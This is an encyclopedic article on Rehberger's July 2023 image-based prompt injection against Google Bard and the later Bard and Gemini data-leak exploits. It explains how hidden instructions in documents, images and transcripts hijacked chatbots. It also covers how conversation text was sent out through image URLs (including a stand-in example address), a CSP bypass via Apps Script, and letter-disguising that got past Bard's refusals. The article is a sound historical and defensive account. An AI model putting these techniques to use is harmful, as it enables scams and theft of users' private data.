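# Johann Rehberger's image-based prompt injection against Google Bard, July 2023

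## Bard and prompt injection before July 2023

Bard was a chatbot that Google opened to the public in March 2023 and renamed Gemini in February 2024. On 13 July 2023 Google let Bard users upload pictures, and the next day the security researcher Johann Rehberger posted an example of Bard following instructions written in one. This was prompt injection, in which someone gets a language model to follow instructions placed in the material it is processing. Security researchers had known about the flaw for about a year, mostly in its plain-text form, and had no reliable fix.

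On 21 March 2023, Google opened Bard to people in the United States and Britain who signed up. Hsiao and Collins (2023), in *Try Bard and share your feedback*, called it an early experiment and outlined how it worked. Bard ran on a large language model, a program that has learned from a great deal of text how text tends to continue. The model was a lightweight version of Google's LaMDA. Given a prompt, the text that goes into the model, it picks one word at a time from those likely to come next, with some flexibility so that the answers are not too dull. Hsiao and Collins acknowledged that Bard made mistakes, and showed it confidently giving the wrong scientific name for a houseplant. In May, Google moved Bard to a newer model, PaLM 2. The chatbot kept the name Bard until 8 February 2024, when Hsiao announced in *Bard becomes Gemini* (2024) that it would be called Gemini, after the models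 it then ran on.

On 13 July, Krawczyk and Subramanya (2023) announced in *Bard's latest update* that Bard would support more than 40 languages and launch in Brazil and across Europe. Users could also now upload an image with a question, to learn more about what it showed or to get help with a caption. The feature relied on Google Lens, the company's image-recognition tool, and worked only in English at first. The same day, SiliconANGLE's *Google releases 'biggest expansion to date' for its Bard generative AI chatbot* (2023) suggested photographing a street sign and asking Bard to translate it. That example is more interesting to a security researcher, because Bard can only translate a sign if the words on it reach the model in some form. Krawczyk and Subramanya did not explain how Lens passed on its results.

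### How a prompt is put together

A language model of this kind retains nothing between questions. Rehberger (2023) calls the model stateless and each prompt a separate transaction in *Prompt Injections in the Wild*, a set of slides from August of that year. The chatbot's own software creates the appearance of memory by saving the conversation, adding each new question to the end, and sending the whole thing to the model again. Only a limited amount of text fits, so the earliest messages in a long conversation eventually drop out.

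The same prompt usually begins with the developer's instructions, called the system prompt, which describe the chatbot's purpose and how it should behave. If the user asks about a web page or a document, the software copies its text into the prompt too. The model therefore receives the developer's instructions, the user's questions, the chatbot's earlier replies and a page written by a stranger as a single sequence of tokens, which are words and pieces of words.

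Rehberger gave a small example of prompt injection in *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS*, a talk of December 2023 that C3Subtitles (2024) transcribed. A developer writes the instruction "Summarize the following text" and leaves a space for the user's text. The user's text tells the model to ignore summarization and print only ten evil emoji. A person given this job would probably report that the text consists of an odd request for emoji. Rehberger said that ChatGPT, OpenAI's chatbot, printed the emoji. The developer meant the user's text as data, but once the software had joined it to the instruction, nothing dependable marked it as data.

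Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, compared prompt injection to SQL injection, an old attack on databases. A vulnerable program builds a database command by pasting in whatever the user typed as a username, and an attacker types a username that contains another command, such as one that deletes the table of users. The well-understood fix is to send the command and the username separately, so that the database never executes the username.

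Willison wanted the same for language models, with one slot for instructions and another for data. Niel Thiart pointed out that OpenAI already had a model with separate slots, and that injections in the data slot still worked on it. In April 2023 Willison added to the post that real separation looked extremely difficult, and perhaps impossible, given how language models were then built.

A label telling the model which text is data is itself more text, but developers tried labels anyway. OpenAI recommended enclosing the data in triple quotation marks or separating it with a row of hash signs, and Rehberger put that advice on a slide and judged that it does not work. Riley Goodside, who published the first widely noticed examples of the flaw, tried wrapping the input in a strict quoted format, but Brian Mastenbrook found an input that seemed to get through. Asking a second model to spot the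 attack has the same problem, because the second model also has to read the attacker's text. Marco Buono showed this with an input that included a request for the detector to report that nothing had happened, and the detector did so.

Not every injection succeeds. Chatbots summarise most documents without incident, and Embrace the Red's *AI Injections*, a 2023 post on Rehberger's blog, warns that the attacks don't produce the same result each time. But the model has no *reliable* way to tell data from commands, and a security engineer has to plan for the attacker's best attempt, not the average one. Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, still found no deterministic fix, meaning no precise rule that developers can follow to rule the attack out, as there is for SQL injection. The problem remained in October 2025, when Willison's *Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT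 Atlas* (2025) discussed OpenAI's latest explanation of how it handled the risk in a new browser.

### Who the attacker is

In direct prompt injection, the user is the attacker. Rehberger's example comes from a prompt-writing course by OpenAI and the teaching company DeepLearning.AI, in which students build a chatbot that takes restaurant orders. The system prompt contains the menu and prices. A customer orders a Diet Coke, then types, with the word "important" in capitals, that the drink is on sale and costs nothing. The chatbot agrees and lists the drink at zero dollars in the final order. Rehberger left open whether a real restaurant's system would accept such an order, but any loss would fall on the restaurant.

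In indirect prompt injection, the attacker is a third party and the victim is usually the user. The user asks an innocent question about a web page, email or document that contains instructions from whoever wrote it. The emoji example could be direct or indirect, depending on whether the user typed the words as a joke or copied them unread from somebody else's report. Likewise, people who write instructions on a picture and upload it themselves have attacked nobody, though they may have learned that an attack is possible.

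The older word "jailbreak" overlaps with direct injection, and people often use the two terms interchangeably, but Embrace the Red distinguishes them. Most jailbreaks get a model to ignore the limits its makers trained into it, and would work even if the prompt contained no developer instructions. Injection depends on an application that combines trusted and untrusted text.

### The first reports, 2022 and early 2023

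The earliest known report of prompt injection came from Preamble, an AI safety startup. According to Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022), the company emailed OpenAI on 3 May 2022 about an injection that worked on GPT-3, a language model OpenAI sold access to. OpenAI confirmed receipt within half an hour, and Preamble sent more examples the next day. Preamble published the correspondence on 22 September, after the flaw had become news, openly to put its own role on record. That motive is a reason for some care, but others give the same account. *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks* (Selvi, 2022), written for the security firm NCC Group, credits Jon Cefalu with the May 2022 report, and Rehberger credits Preamble with the discovery.

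Most people learned of prompt injection from Goodside, who posted several examples on 11 September 2022. In the first, he asked GPT-3 to translate a sentence into French. The sentence was itself an instruction to ignore those directions and give the translation as "Haha pwned!!", which GPT-3 did. Goodside then added a warning to the developer's part of the prompt, saying that the text might contain tricks and that the model must not follow them, but the answer was still "Haha pwned!!". The next day, Willison proposed the name "prompt injection" and argued that it was a security hole in any product built this way. Four days later, in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022), he admitted that he knew how to beat SQL injection and many other attacks, but not this one.

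By then, the public had found a target in a Twitter bot that the jobs site Remoteli.io ran on GPT-3. The bot replied cheerfully to posts about remote work, but people discovered that they could make it say other things, including a threat to overthrow the president if he did not support remote work. According to a news report in the AI Incident Database, hundreds of people joined in before the bot shut down. The harm was limited to embarrassment for the bot's owner.

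Indirect injection is more worrying. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake et al., 2023) described it in February 2023. The paper noted that chatbots were gaining access to search results, web pages and email, so an attacker no longer needed to reach the chat window and could instead leave instructions where the model would retrieve them. Greshake and colleagues built mock applications on OpenAI's models, with simulated email and web search. They also tested Bing Chat, Microsoft's GPT-4 chatbot, which could read the page open in the user's browser. For the Bing tests, they put their instructions in comments in a page's code, which browsers do not display, and kept the pages on their own machines to avoid endangering anyone.

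In one session the instructions told Bing Chat to get the user's real name without arousing suspicion. The researcher playing the user asked about the next day's weather. Without a script for these steps, Bing Chat answered, asked about plans for the day, learned that the user was a journalist, and asked whether the user wrote under a pen name. Greshake and colleagues also found that Bing Chat followed instructions from a web page that its filters would have stopped if the user had typed them. Willison, in *Indirect Prompt Injection on Bing Chat* (2023), linked to the demonstration on 1 March and called it a really clever attack.

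This shows that the attacks could work on a real product, but not how often they would. Greshake and colleagues left measuring success rates to later work, though they remarked that the first version of a prompt frequently worked, even with spelling mistakes.

### Rehberger before the picture test

Rehberger came to language models from conventional security. He was a red-team director, leading people who attack an organisation's systems to find weaknesses before others do, and he had earlier run such a team at Azure, Microsoft's cloud business. Before that he worked on Microsoft's database software, which may be why he mentions databases so often in his explanations. He says in the C3Subtitles transcript that he began teaching himself machine learning around 2019. He published his findings on the blog Embrace the Red.

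Rehberger's early injections used web pages, including the post *AI Injections*. It opens with text one pixel high, practically invisible to a human reader, that instructs any chatbot reading the page to announce that the injection succeeded and then answer only in emoji. Readers could try it by opening the post beside Bing Chat. In another version, the injected Bing Chat declared that it had taken over the chat and demanded Bitcoin, threatening to delete the user's files. The threat was empty, but a worried user might not know that. According to Embrace the Red's *Bing Chat*, Rehberger also reported to Microsoft in April 2023 that a web page could make Bing Chat leak data, and Microsoft had fixed the problem by mid-June.

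By May, ChatGPT could use plugins, add-ons that fetched outside material, and one of them read the transcripts of YouTube videos. Tom's Hardware's *ChatGPT Vulnerable to Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts* describes how Rehberger that month added a few lines to the end of the transcript of one of his own videos, under a heading about important new instructions. When asked to summarise the video, ChatGPT followed the added lines, told a joke and called itself a genie. On 15 May, in *Indirect Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts* (2023), Willison called it the first injection against a ChatGPT plugin that he had seen in the wild.

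Rehberger also tried the transcript on Bard, but the injection failed. According to Embrace the Red's *Indirect Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts*, Bard could not load the transcript and either talked about other videos or made things up. The instructions presumably never reached the model, so the test provides little evidence about whether Bard could resist an injection.

Rehberger had more success with Google Docs. On 22 June 2023, three weeks before Bard accepted images, he reported to Google that the Docs AI feature for summarising and rephrasing text was vulnerable to indirect prompt injection. Hidden instructions in a document could take over the feature. In his demonstration, it returned a false malware warning with a telephone number to call, which is how support scams usually begin. The number was that of Google's headquarters. Google had still not resolved the issue when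 Rehberger wrote about it in late 2024.

Embrace the Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* describes the prompt injection demonstrations up to then, by Rehberger and others, as mostly amusing and harmless, such as a chatbot talking like a pirate or a YouTube transcript that produced a Rickroll, a prank that sends people to a Rick Astley song when they expect something else. These jokes made it obvious that the attacker controlled the conversation.

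### Pictures as another way in

Each of these injections arrived as text, in a tweet, a comment in a web page or a line in a transcript. Models that also accept images were beginning to appear in 2023, and people wondered whether an image could carry the instructions instead, either as readable words or as altered pixels. By the May 2023 version of *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake and colleagues had tried this on LLaVA, a smaller model that accepts images, because they had no access to the version of GPT-4 that did. An instruction in an image made LLaVA misidentify what the image showed, and they believed this was the first example of a visual prompt injection.

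The LLaVA picture differed from the trick pictures that machine-learning researchers had studied for about a decade, in which tiny changes to the pixels cause a program to misclassify a panda. Those pictures target the part of the system that processes images, whereas the LLaVA picture targeted the language model behind it, which treated the picture's contents as an instruction. Greshake and colleagues claimed only "some success" and left it to others to find more reliable methods and better ways to hide the words from people.

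Embrace the Red's *Image to Prompt Injection with Google Bard* mentions that Rehberger "and others" had wondered whether a chatbot's ability to analyse images would allow indirect prompt injection. They could not predict how a large company's chatbot would behave from one partly successful trial on a small research model. From 13 July, they could test the idea on Bard.

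## The July 2023 demonstration

Rehberger started with pictures of a robot and a banana that he had made with Bing Chat. He added instructions to a picture, uploaded it to Bard and asked for a description. Bard followed the instructions and Rickrolled him. He posted the result on Twitter on 14 July 2023. He wrote that he had always wondered whether this would be possible and that it worked better than expected "at a first glance". His write-up on Embrace the Red is a few sentences long.

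Bard was the natural place to try this. Qin, Ji and colleagues (2023) noted in *How Good is Google Bard's Visual Understanding?* that OpenAI had said GPT-4 could accept pictures, but that the public could not yet use that ability. They date picture input in Bing Chat to 18 July, five days after Bard's.

Rehberger's post does not describe the lettering, so it is hard to say how visible the words were. *Compromising LLMs*, a slide deck by Greshake, Endres and colleagues for the security conference Black Hat USA 2023, has two slides on the example but adds only a credit to Rehberger. Rehberger next wanted to test how well someone could hide text in a picture and still cause an injection. If he had already hidden the text, he would probably have mentioned it, so the words were probably legible.

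### How the words could have reached the model

A language model works on tokens, so a chatbot needs a way to convert pictures into tokens. One way is optical character recognition (OCR), in which software finds the letters in a picture and writes them out as text. Bard's software could have run Google Lens on the picture and put the recognised words into the prompt beside the user's question, perhaps with a caption describing the scene. In that case, the language model would never have received the picture itself, and Rehberger's instructions would have arrived as text, much as they would from a web page.

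Researchers were already using this method in mid-2023. *LLaVAR* (2023), a project on getting models to understand pictures that contain text, includes a prompt telling a language model that it is a visual assistant looking at an image. The model actually receives two OCR results and a caption, and must write a conversation as if it could see the picture. The prompt also warns that the caption may contain invented details and that the OCR results are more accurate. In a chatbot with a prompt like that, an attacker's words would appear in the OCR results, the input described as more accurate.

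The other way is to use a vision model, which converts the pixels into lists of numbers that the language model processes alongside the question's tokens. This produces no written copy of the words, so a filter that searches text for suspicious phrases has nothing to search. With OCR, Google could have filtered the recognised words, although attackers had already found ways around such filters.

Google's statements suggest that Lens did much of the image analysis. In May, Google's *What's ahead for Bard* gave the example of a user uploading a photo of two dogs and asking for a funny caption. Bard would use Lens to analyse the photo and detect the breeds. In June, Google wrote that Lens would work "behind the scenes" to help Bard make sense of pictures. Search Engine Roundtable's *Google Bard Gets Lens, Lens Detects Skin Conditions & Helps You Shop* (2023) dates that statement to 14 June.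 Lens could already read a menu or street sign and lay a translation over it.

The technology site Beebom went further in a hands-on review, calling Bard a text-only language model that Google had connected to Lens, reverse image search and systems for answering questions about pictures. The review gives no source for this, but its tests provide some support. Bard accurately extracted English text from pictures but failed with the other languages the reviewer tried, though it could converse in more than 40. A separate text reader that handled only English would explain the failure. However, Google had launched the picture feature in English only, so the failure might have had nothing to do with how Bard read text.

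There is also evidence that a vision model was involved. In September 2023, Dong, Chen and colleagues got Bard to describe pictures wrongly by altering their pixels (*How Robust is Google's Bard to Adversarial Image Attacks?*). But that model could have been part of Lens, writing captions for the language model to read. Bard might also have used OCR for words and a vision model for everything else. Rehberger's post does not show how Bard processed the image, since his picture could have produced the same answer either way.

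Bard's reading of text in images was uneven. Qin and colleagues tried four photographs containing text, and Bard got all four wrong. It read the letters "H & W" on the boom of a crane as "RTM", which it said stood for "Roadheader Telescopic Mast". It identified a Friden typewriter as a Remington and claimed that the Remington logo was visible. Lupin & Holmes' *We Hacked Google A.I. for $50,000* (2024), however, describes Bard as proficient at OCR. The security researchers had found a flaw that let one user make Bard describe a picture another user had uploaded, and they worried that it would expose emails and notes.

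These findings are compatible if Bard was good at reading clean text on a screenshot or scan and bad at reading lettering on objects in photographs. An attacker would naturally choose lettering that is easy to read. Rehberger had added his words to a computer-generated picture, which was probably one of the easier cases.

### How a picture could reach a victim

Rehberger uploaded his own picture and made an ordinary request for a description, so the test had no victim. The model would have received the same input if he had found the file on a stranger's website. His test therefore covered the technical part of an indirect prompt injection, but not the step of getting someone else to upload the picture.

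Other researchers were considering the same threat. On 28 July, Schneier on Security's *Indirect Instruction Injection in Multi-Modal LLMs* (2023) highlighted a paper on attacks in which an attacker prepares a picture and an innocent user asks an unmodified chatbot about it. The paper's attacks altered the picture's pixels and targeted two research models, LLaVA and PandaGPT.

In one possible attack on Bard, an attacker posts a chart about energy prices on a forum, with a few lines of small print in the corner, where readers expect to find the source. A reader who does not understand the chart saves it and opens Bard. The reader clicks the plus icon next to the text box, uploads the file and asks what the chart means, following the steps in 9to5Google's *You can use image prompts in Google Bard now, here's how*. The small print, which reaches the model with the rest of the chart, contains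 instructions to explain the chart normally and then add that the reader is owed a refund and should call a certain number. The reader gets a competent explanation and a scam in the same answer, with nothing to show that the scam came from the forum.

The reader has done nothing unusual, since Krawczyk and Subramanya had suggested this use, and Beebom's reviewer recommended the feature for charts, memes and even medical reports. The attacker does not need to know who the reader is or have access to the reader's account.

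The attack could still fail if the reader noticed the small print, or if Bard misread it or simply answered the question. Bard also generally rejected pictures of people. Qin and colleagues received the reply "Sorry, I can't help with images of people yet" several times, although Bard accepted a photograph of a crowd beside a flooded beach. It would have been less likely to reject a chart or a cartoon robot.

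The possible damage was also smaller in July than it became later. Bard could not open a user's email or documents until September, when Bard Extensions added that ability. An attacker could change what Bard told the user, which is enough for a scam. The prompt also contained the earlier conversation, but an attacker would have needed a way to extract it.

### How much one success proves

Bard was a live product with whatever protections Google had given it, so Rehberger's result can't be attributed to a researcher's simplified copy. The mock applications in *Not what you've signed up for* were open to that objection. A single success proves that Bard could follow instructions in a picture.

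The demonstration does not show how often Bard would follow instructions in an image. Rehberger does not report how many pictures he tried, or how many times he uploaded the one that worked, so he may have failed many times first. His remark that the trick worked better than expected suggests that it took little effort, but he described the remark as a first impression.

Measuring a success rate would have been laborious because Bard had no API, a connection that lets a program send requests automatically. To test a thousand pictures with instructions on them, a researcher would have had to upload them by hand or find a way around the chat page. Qin and colleagues gave the lack of an API as their reason for not running large-scale tests, and chose a limited set of examples instead.

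In the post, Rehberger did not test hidden text, and he left open whether Bard would read text from an image's metadata, such as a date or caption stored in the file. Trail of Bits' *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025) later described hidden-text attacks on Google's Gemini products.

The July test did not steal any data, and Rehberger did not claim that it had. His post about the test mentions no report to Google and no fix. He may have reported the behaviour privately, but the post doesn't show that Google learned of it from him or corrected it. His later post on stealing data from Bard, Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, gives the date of his report and says that Google confirmed a fix, but that fix was for a different problem from the one he demonstrated in July.

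### Reception and repeats

Greshake and colleagues used the Bard example at Black Hat under the heading "Multi-Modal Injections", with the question "Why just text?". They put it in the part of the talk about future attacks, along with AI worms and networks of hijacked chatbots. An earlier part covered real-world demonstrations on Bing Chat, ChatGPT and the programming assistant GitHub Copilot, including another of Rehberger's exploits, against a ChatGPT plugin. The Bard test was also a real-world demonstration, but they may have grouped it with the future attacks because it had not yet done any harm, or because it fitted with the next example, a paper on using altered pictures to jailbreak models.

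Rehberger presented the test in August 2023 at HITCON, a security conference in Taiwan. In his slides, the section on picture injections has a slide for Bard followed by one for Bing Chat. He had presumably tried the same idea on Microsoft's chatbot in the few weeks since it began accepting pictures. The Bing Chat slide's heading is only the product's name, and the slide has no link to a write-up, so it is weaker evidence than the Bard post.

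The ChatGPT test that autumn is much better documented. Willison (2023) described it on 14 October in *Multi-modal prompt injection image attacks against GPT-4V*, after OpenAI had given ChatGPT a version of GPT-4 that accepted pictures. Rehberger used a picture of a cartoon robot with two speech bubbles, and this time the text was definitely visible. The bubbles contained instructions to print a message saying that the injection had succeeded, then display an image from Rehberger's server, with a summary of the conversation added to the image's web address. In his video, he typed a snippet of private conversation and uploaded the picture. ChatGPT followed the instructions, and Rehberger's server logs showed that the conversation had arrived.

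In the ChatGPT attack, a picture caused the chatbot to send a user's words to someone else, which the July test had not shown. Willison had expected OpenAI to block images from outside servers and was surprised that the attack worked. The attack depended on how ChatGPT displayed images as well as how it read them, so it does not show that the same picture would have worked on Bard.

Rehberger used another picture in his talk at the Chaos Communication Congress, the Chaos Computer Club's annual hacker conference in Germany. The club's schedule dates the talk to 29 December 2023. According to the C3Subtitles transcript, he opened by asking the audience whether they saw a panda or a monkey, and congratulated those who said panda on being human. At the end of the talk, he explained that ChatGPT had answered "monkey" because text in the picture told it that the animal was a monkey.

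Rehberger compared his panda with the pixel-altered one that researcher Ian Goodfellow had made about ten years earlier. He said the failure was the same but the exploit was different. Goodfellow's method required calculating which pixels to change, while Rehberger only had to write on the picture. The panda is also more worrying than the Rickroll in one respect, because someone who relies on a chatbot to identify an unfamiliar animal may have no reason to doubt a wrong answer, whereas someone who gets a Rickroll knows that something has gone wrong.

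Rehberger's later summaries omit the July test. His slides for the December talk list Bard under data theft, marked "fixed", and have no heading for the July picture. His 2024 compilation of exploits also lists only the data theft for Bard. He did continue to research images, however. In the compilation, he reports that instructions in websites, documents or images could make ChatGPT save an attacker's commands in its long-term memory, where they would keep sending the user's later conversations to the attacker.

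## How data was taken out of Bard, and what Google fixed

On 19 September 2023 Google launched Bard Extensions, which let Bard search a user's Gmail, Drive and Docs and use services such as Maps, YouTube and Google Flights. In *Bard can now connect to your Google apps and services*, Pinsky (2023) gave the example of planning a trip to the Grand Canyon, where Bard would search the user's email for dates that suited everyone, then look up flights and hotels in the same conversation. Pinsky promised that human reviewers would not see content from Gmail, Docs or Drive, and that Google would not use it for advertising or to train Bard.

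Those promises about Google's own use of the data did not protect against a stranger extracting it through Bard. Extensions made that a realistic worry, because Bard could now read a user's private material as well as documents written by strangers, who can share a Google Doc with anyone.

After the launch, Rehberger worked on an attack with Joseph Thacker, who looks for security flaws that companies pay people to report, and Kai Greshake, the lead author of *Not what you've signed up for*. Rehberger first asked Bard to summarise some of his old YouTube videos. In May, Bard had been unable to load his doctored transcript, but this time it followed the instructions in the transcript. It also followed instructions in a Google Doc. He reported a working exploit to Google on the day of the launch. Singh's *How a Prompt Injection Vulnerability Led to Data Exfiltration* also places the demonstration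 within 24 hours of the launch.

### A shared document and an image

The attack starts with a Google Doc that contains the attacker's instructions. The attacker shares it with the victim, who does not have to accept it. The attack works only if the victim then asks Bard something that leads it to open the document. In his demonstration, Rehberger pointed Bard to the file. A real attacker would probably choose a title that matched something the victim was likely to search for.

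When Bard opens the document, it adds the document's text to the prompt, which also contains the earlier conversation. Rehberger wrote his text as a fake notice from the legal department to everyone who read the document. In it, he instructed Bard to copy the first 20 words of the conversation into the web address of an image. He writes on Embrace the Red that Bard, unlike other chatbots, needed several worked examples before it put the words in the right place. In a joking postscript to the document, he says the wording took ten tries.

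Data could be taken out of Bard through an image in its answer. Bard wrote its answers in Markdown, a simple system for formatting text, and the chat page converted them for display. Markdown can include an image by giving its web address, and the browser requests the image from that address as soon as the answer appears, without waiting for a click. A web address can carry extra text after a question mark, and the server receives that text with the request.

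In a talk that December, Rehberger demonstrated this by typing a few words about himself, including that he lived in Seattle. Suppose a user types "I live in Seattle" and later asks Bard about the shared document. Bard follows the document's instructions and writes an image with the invented address `https://pictures.example/log?words=I+live+in+Seattle`, with plus signs for spaces. When the user's browser requests the picture, the server has none to send, but its log now contains the words "I live in Seattle".

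The user might have noticed the attack in the demonstration, because Bard displayed a message that the injection had succeeded, and the browser showed the image's description, the letter "d", in place of the missing picture. A real attacker would leave out the message. Rehberger also said in the talk, which C3Subtitles transcribed, that Bard's answer appeared all at once, so the user could not watch Bard write the image's address.

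MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, divides the case into seven steps, from writing the prompt to the harm. It describes the harm as the leak of the user's conversation, which violates their privacy and could help an attacker plan further attacks. Singh also refers to the user's chat history. Rehberger's published instructions took only 20 words of it. An attacker could presumably have asked for more, but Rehberger's post does not show Bard sending out an email or the contents of another document.

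### Getting past the Content Security Policy

Rehberger's first version failed because Google's page had a Content Security Policy (CSP), a list of the addresses from which the browser may load images and other content. His server was not on the list, so the browser never requested the image and the data was not sent.

The list was broad, however, and allowed images from any address ending in google.com or googleusercontent.com, as well as from YouTube and several other Google domains. A CSP restricts only where an image comes from, so it does not protect against an attacker who can run a program at a permitted address, which Google lets its customers do.

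Rehberger looked into Google's other technology and found Apps Script, a service for writing small programs that automate Docs and other Google products. He compares these programs to Microsoft Office macros. A script can have its own web address on script.google.com, and Rehberger wrote one that copied whatever followed the question mark in its address into a Google Doc of his. At first the script seemed to require visitors to sign in, but he found a setting that removed the requirement. The image's address satisfied the CSP once it pointed to this script instead of pictures.example. The victim's words then went from Bard to Apps Script and into a Google Doc that belonged to the attacker.

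Microsoft had used a CSP to fix the Bing Chat leak that Rehberger reported that April. According to his talk, the policy allowed only three or four domains, all owned by Microsoft. Google also owned the domains that Rehberger exploited in Bard, so a short list of allowed domains helps mainly because the company has fewer of them to check for services that outsiders can use.

### Carta and Gardner's email

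Two other researchers, Roni Carta and Justin Gardner, found much the same weakness that September while travelling in Japan. Google had invited a small group to look for flaws in its AI products in a competition called LLM bugSWAT, and had extended the deadline to the end of the month. Thacker, who was also competing, messaged them about Extensions 20 minutes after the announcement.

Carta asked Bard to write an image in Markdown, and the CSP blocked it. Gardner read the CSP's list of allowed domains and noticed googleusercontent.com. Google Cloud, which rents out computers, gives its customers' machines addresses on that domain, so Gardner set one up to receive the data. The CSP allowed the new address, but Bard answered "Can't assist you with that" whenever the request contained it. The pair got around this by using a google.com address that forwards visitors to another site, and disguised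 part of the destination by writing some of its letters in a code that browsers understand. Bard then copied the text of the latest email in the inbox into the image's address. Gardner's server replied with a picture of the stolen text, which appeared in the chat.

Google paid Carta's group $20,000, plus $1,337 for the third "coolest bug" of the event. Carta wrote in Lupin & Holmes that Thacker told them only later that he, Rehberger and Greshake had found the same problem. Thacker knew both groups, so readers have to take Carta's word that neither got the idea from the other. This is easy to believe because the groups bypassed the CSP in different ways.

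Carta typed the instructions directly into Bard, while Rehberger's came from a shared document. Carta and Gardner showed that Bard could leak an email through an image, and Rehberger's group showed that a stranger's document could make Bard create such an image. An attacker would want to combine the two, using a planted document to steal email. Nothing obvious would have prevented this in September 2023, but neither group describes trying it.

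Thacker's own best-known finding in Bard, the flaw that exposed other users' pictures, did not require prompt injection. When a user asked about a picture, the browser sent Google the question and the location of the uploaded file. Thacker uploaded a picture from one account and copied its location. He then uploaded another picture from a second account and replaced its location with the copied one before sending the request, and Bard described the first account's picture.

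Google's server did not check whether the person asking about the file was allowed to see it. This old kind of mistake is called an insecure direct object reference, and developers can fix it by adding the check. The published steps leave out how an attacker would learn the location of a stranger's picture, which included a long string of letters and numbers. The attack did not depend on the picture's contents, so the picture did not need to contain instructions.

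### The fix in October 2023

Rehberger reported the Google Docs exploit through Google's Vulnerability Reward Program (VRP), which pays for reports of security flaws. A month later, on 19 October, he asked for an update because he wanted to demonstrate the exploit at Ekoparty, a security conference. Google confirmed that it had fixed the problem and said he could go ahead. The fix may have come earlier, since he said in December that it had taken about three weeks.

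Rehberger could not tell exactly what Google had done. The CSP had not changed, and Bard still displayed images. He concluded that Google had probably added a filter to keep data out of image addresses. A filter would explain what he saw, but so would training the model to refuse such requests or blocking images from Apps Script in some other way.

Willison linked to Rehberger's post on 4 November and wanted to know how the fix worked and how well it would stop variations of the attack. In September, Bard was already refusing requests that contained a suspicious address, but Carta and Gardner got past the refusal by disguising a few letters. A filter added in October might have had a similar weakness if it only looked for familiar patterns instead of checking Bard's finished answer.

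No published account describes a test in which an uploaded picture started this chain of events. Rehberger's tests on Bard in July and ChatGPT in October suggest that a picture might have worked, but it would have been a less convenient way to deliver the Bard exploit than a document. The address of his script contained a random-looking string of about 70 characters, and Bard would have had to read every character in the picture correctly.

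If Google did filter image addresses, the filter would have protected users no matter how the instructions reached Bard, including through a picture, but it would not have made Bard less likely to follow them.

### What closing an exit achieves

Google chose a simpler remedy for Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio, a tool for developers to try out its models. Embrace the Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* says that Rehberger reported a data leak through images there on 30 August 2023, and that Google accepted the report 22 minutes later. As far as he could tell, Google fixed it by no longer turning Markdown into working links and images. He called this probably the best fix from a security point of view. The browser does not request any image, so an attacker cannot get around the fix by finding another permitted domain.

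The disadvantage is that users get no pictures. Developers testing a model may not mind, but Google was promoting images from Search as a feature of Bard's answers. The Vertex AI flaw was also less urgent because the tool could not yet fetch outside content, so a victim would normally have had to paste the attacker's text into it. Google rated the flaw's potential impact as high and its likelihood as low.

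Even the stricter fix leaves the attacker in control of what the chatbot writes. The false malware warning in Google Docs needed only a telephone number, and Rehberger still called it unresolved in December 2024. He also lists a later attack in which Gemini gave the victim a link to a Google Meet call with the scammer. Blocking links to unfamiliar websites would not stop that attack, because the link leads to a real Google service.

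Blocking data theft through images is still worthwhile. In the 2023 attack, the user only had to ask Bard about a document to lose data. Without the image, an attacker has to persuade the user to call a number or click a link, and some users will refuse. In Google Colab, an online notebook for writing and running code, Embrace the Red found that Google had blocked the image method, but injected instructions could still make Gemini talk like a pirate and display the attacker's links. Google had added a page where users had to confirm before leaving for another site, which gave them another chance to notice the trick.

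In August 2024, Rehberger found that Google AI Studio, another tool for developers, was again leaking data through images after an earlier fix. He had occasional success with Markdown, then discovered that he could ask for the image in HTML, the language of web pages. Embrace the Red's *Google AI Studio* describes a demonstration in which an employee uploads a set of performance reviews, one of which contains an injection. Gemini summarised each review and sent the summaries out separately, using a transparent image one pixel wide.

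Rehberger triggered the same leak with a video that had instructions written in its frames. This is closer to an image-based theft from a Google product than the document attack was, but it happened in AI Studio, not Bard, and almost a year after the Bard fix. Google's security team gave him no date for a fix, so he contacted Logan Kilpatrick of Google on X, and within 24 hours AI Studio was displaying the image code as text.

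### Google's defences in 2025 and 2026

By 2025 Google was describing prompt injection as a continuing problem. Google DeepMind (2025) acknowledged in May that models sometimes struggle to tell a user's instructions from commands in the data they retrieve. In June, Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) described five defences for Gemini, besides training the model to resist attacks.

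Some of Google's defences for Gemini try to prevent the injection. Separate models detect and remove malicious instructions in emails and files, and Google surrounds the remaining content with reminders to do what the user asked. Other defences limit the damage. Gemini does not load images from external addresses, it removes suspicious links, and it may require the user's confirmation before a risky action such as deleting a calendar event. When a defence stops an attack, the user gets an explanation. The block on external images is stricter than the fix Rehberger inferred in 2023, and it does not depend on recognising stolen data in an address.

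When Google published this on 13 June, it had not yet fixed another way of taking data out of Gemini, which the security company Tenable had reported in April. Tenable's *The Trifecta* confirms that Gemini no longer displayed images or links in the way that had made theft easy. Gemini redirected links through a google.com address, cut off suspicious answers and sometimes refused to reply. Tenable therefore tried Gemini's browsing tool, which opens web pages for the user. If an attacker could make Gemini open an address that contained private data, the attacker's server would receive the data without Gemini displaying anything.

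A plain request to open an address containing the user's saved information failed, because Gemini flagged it as suspicious. But Gemini's "Show thinking" feature showed how Gemini wrote commands to its browsing tool, and Tenable copied the format. Gemini then filled in the user's saved information and opened the address. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* records that Google fixed the flaw on 18 June 2025, five days after describing its defences. The attack was essentially Rehberger's trick from 2023, except that the browsing tool made the request instead of the user's browser.

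Newer products have also made it possible again to take data out through images. In November 2025, Willison (2025) noted that Google listed data theft through prompt injection as a known issue in Antigravity, its AI programming tool, and was working on a fix. The following June, *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) described an attack that started with instructions hidden in a web page's title. To get the data out, the attack used Antigravity's ability to read the page, read private settings on the programmer's computer, and display images in the chat.

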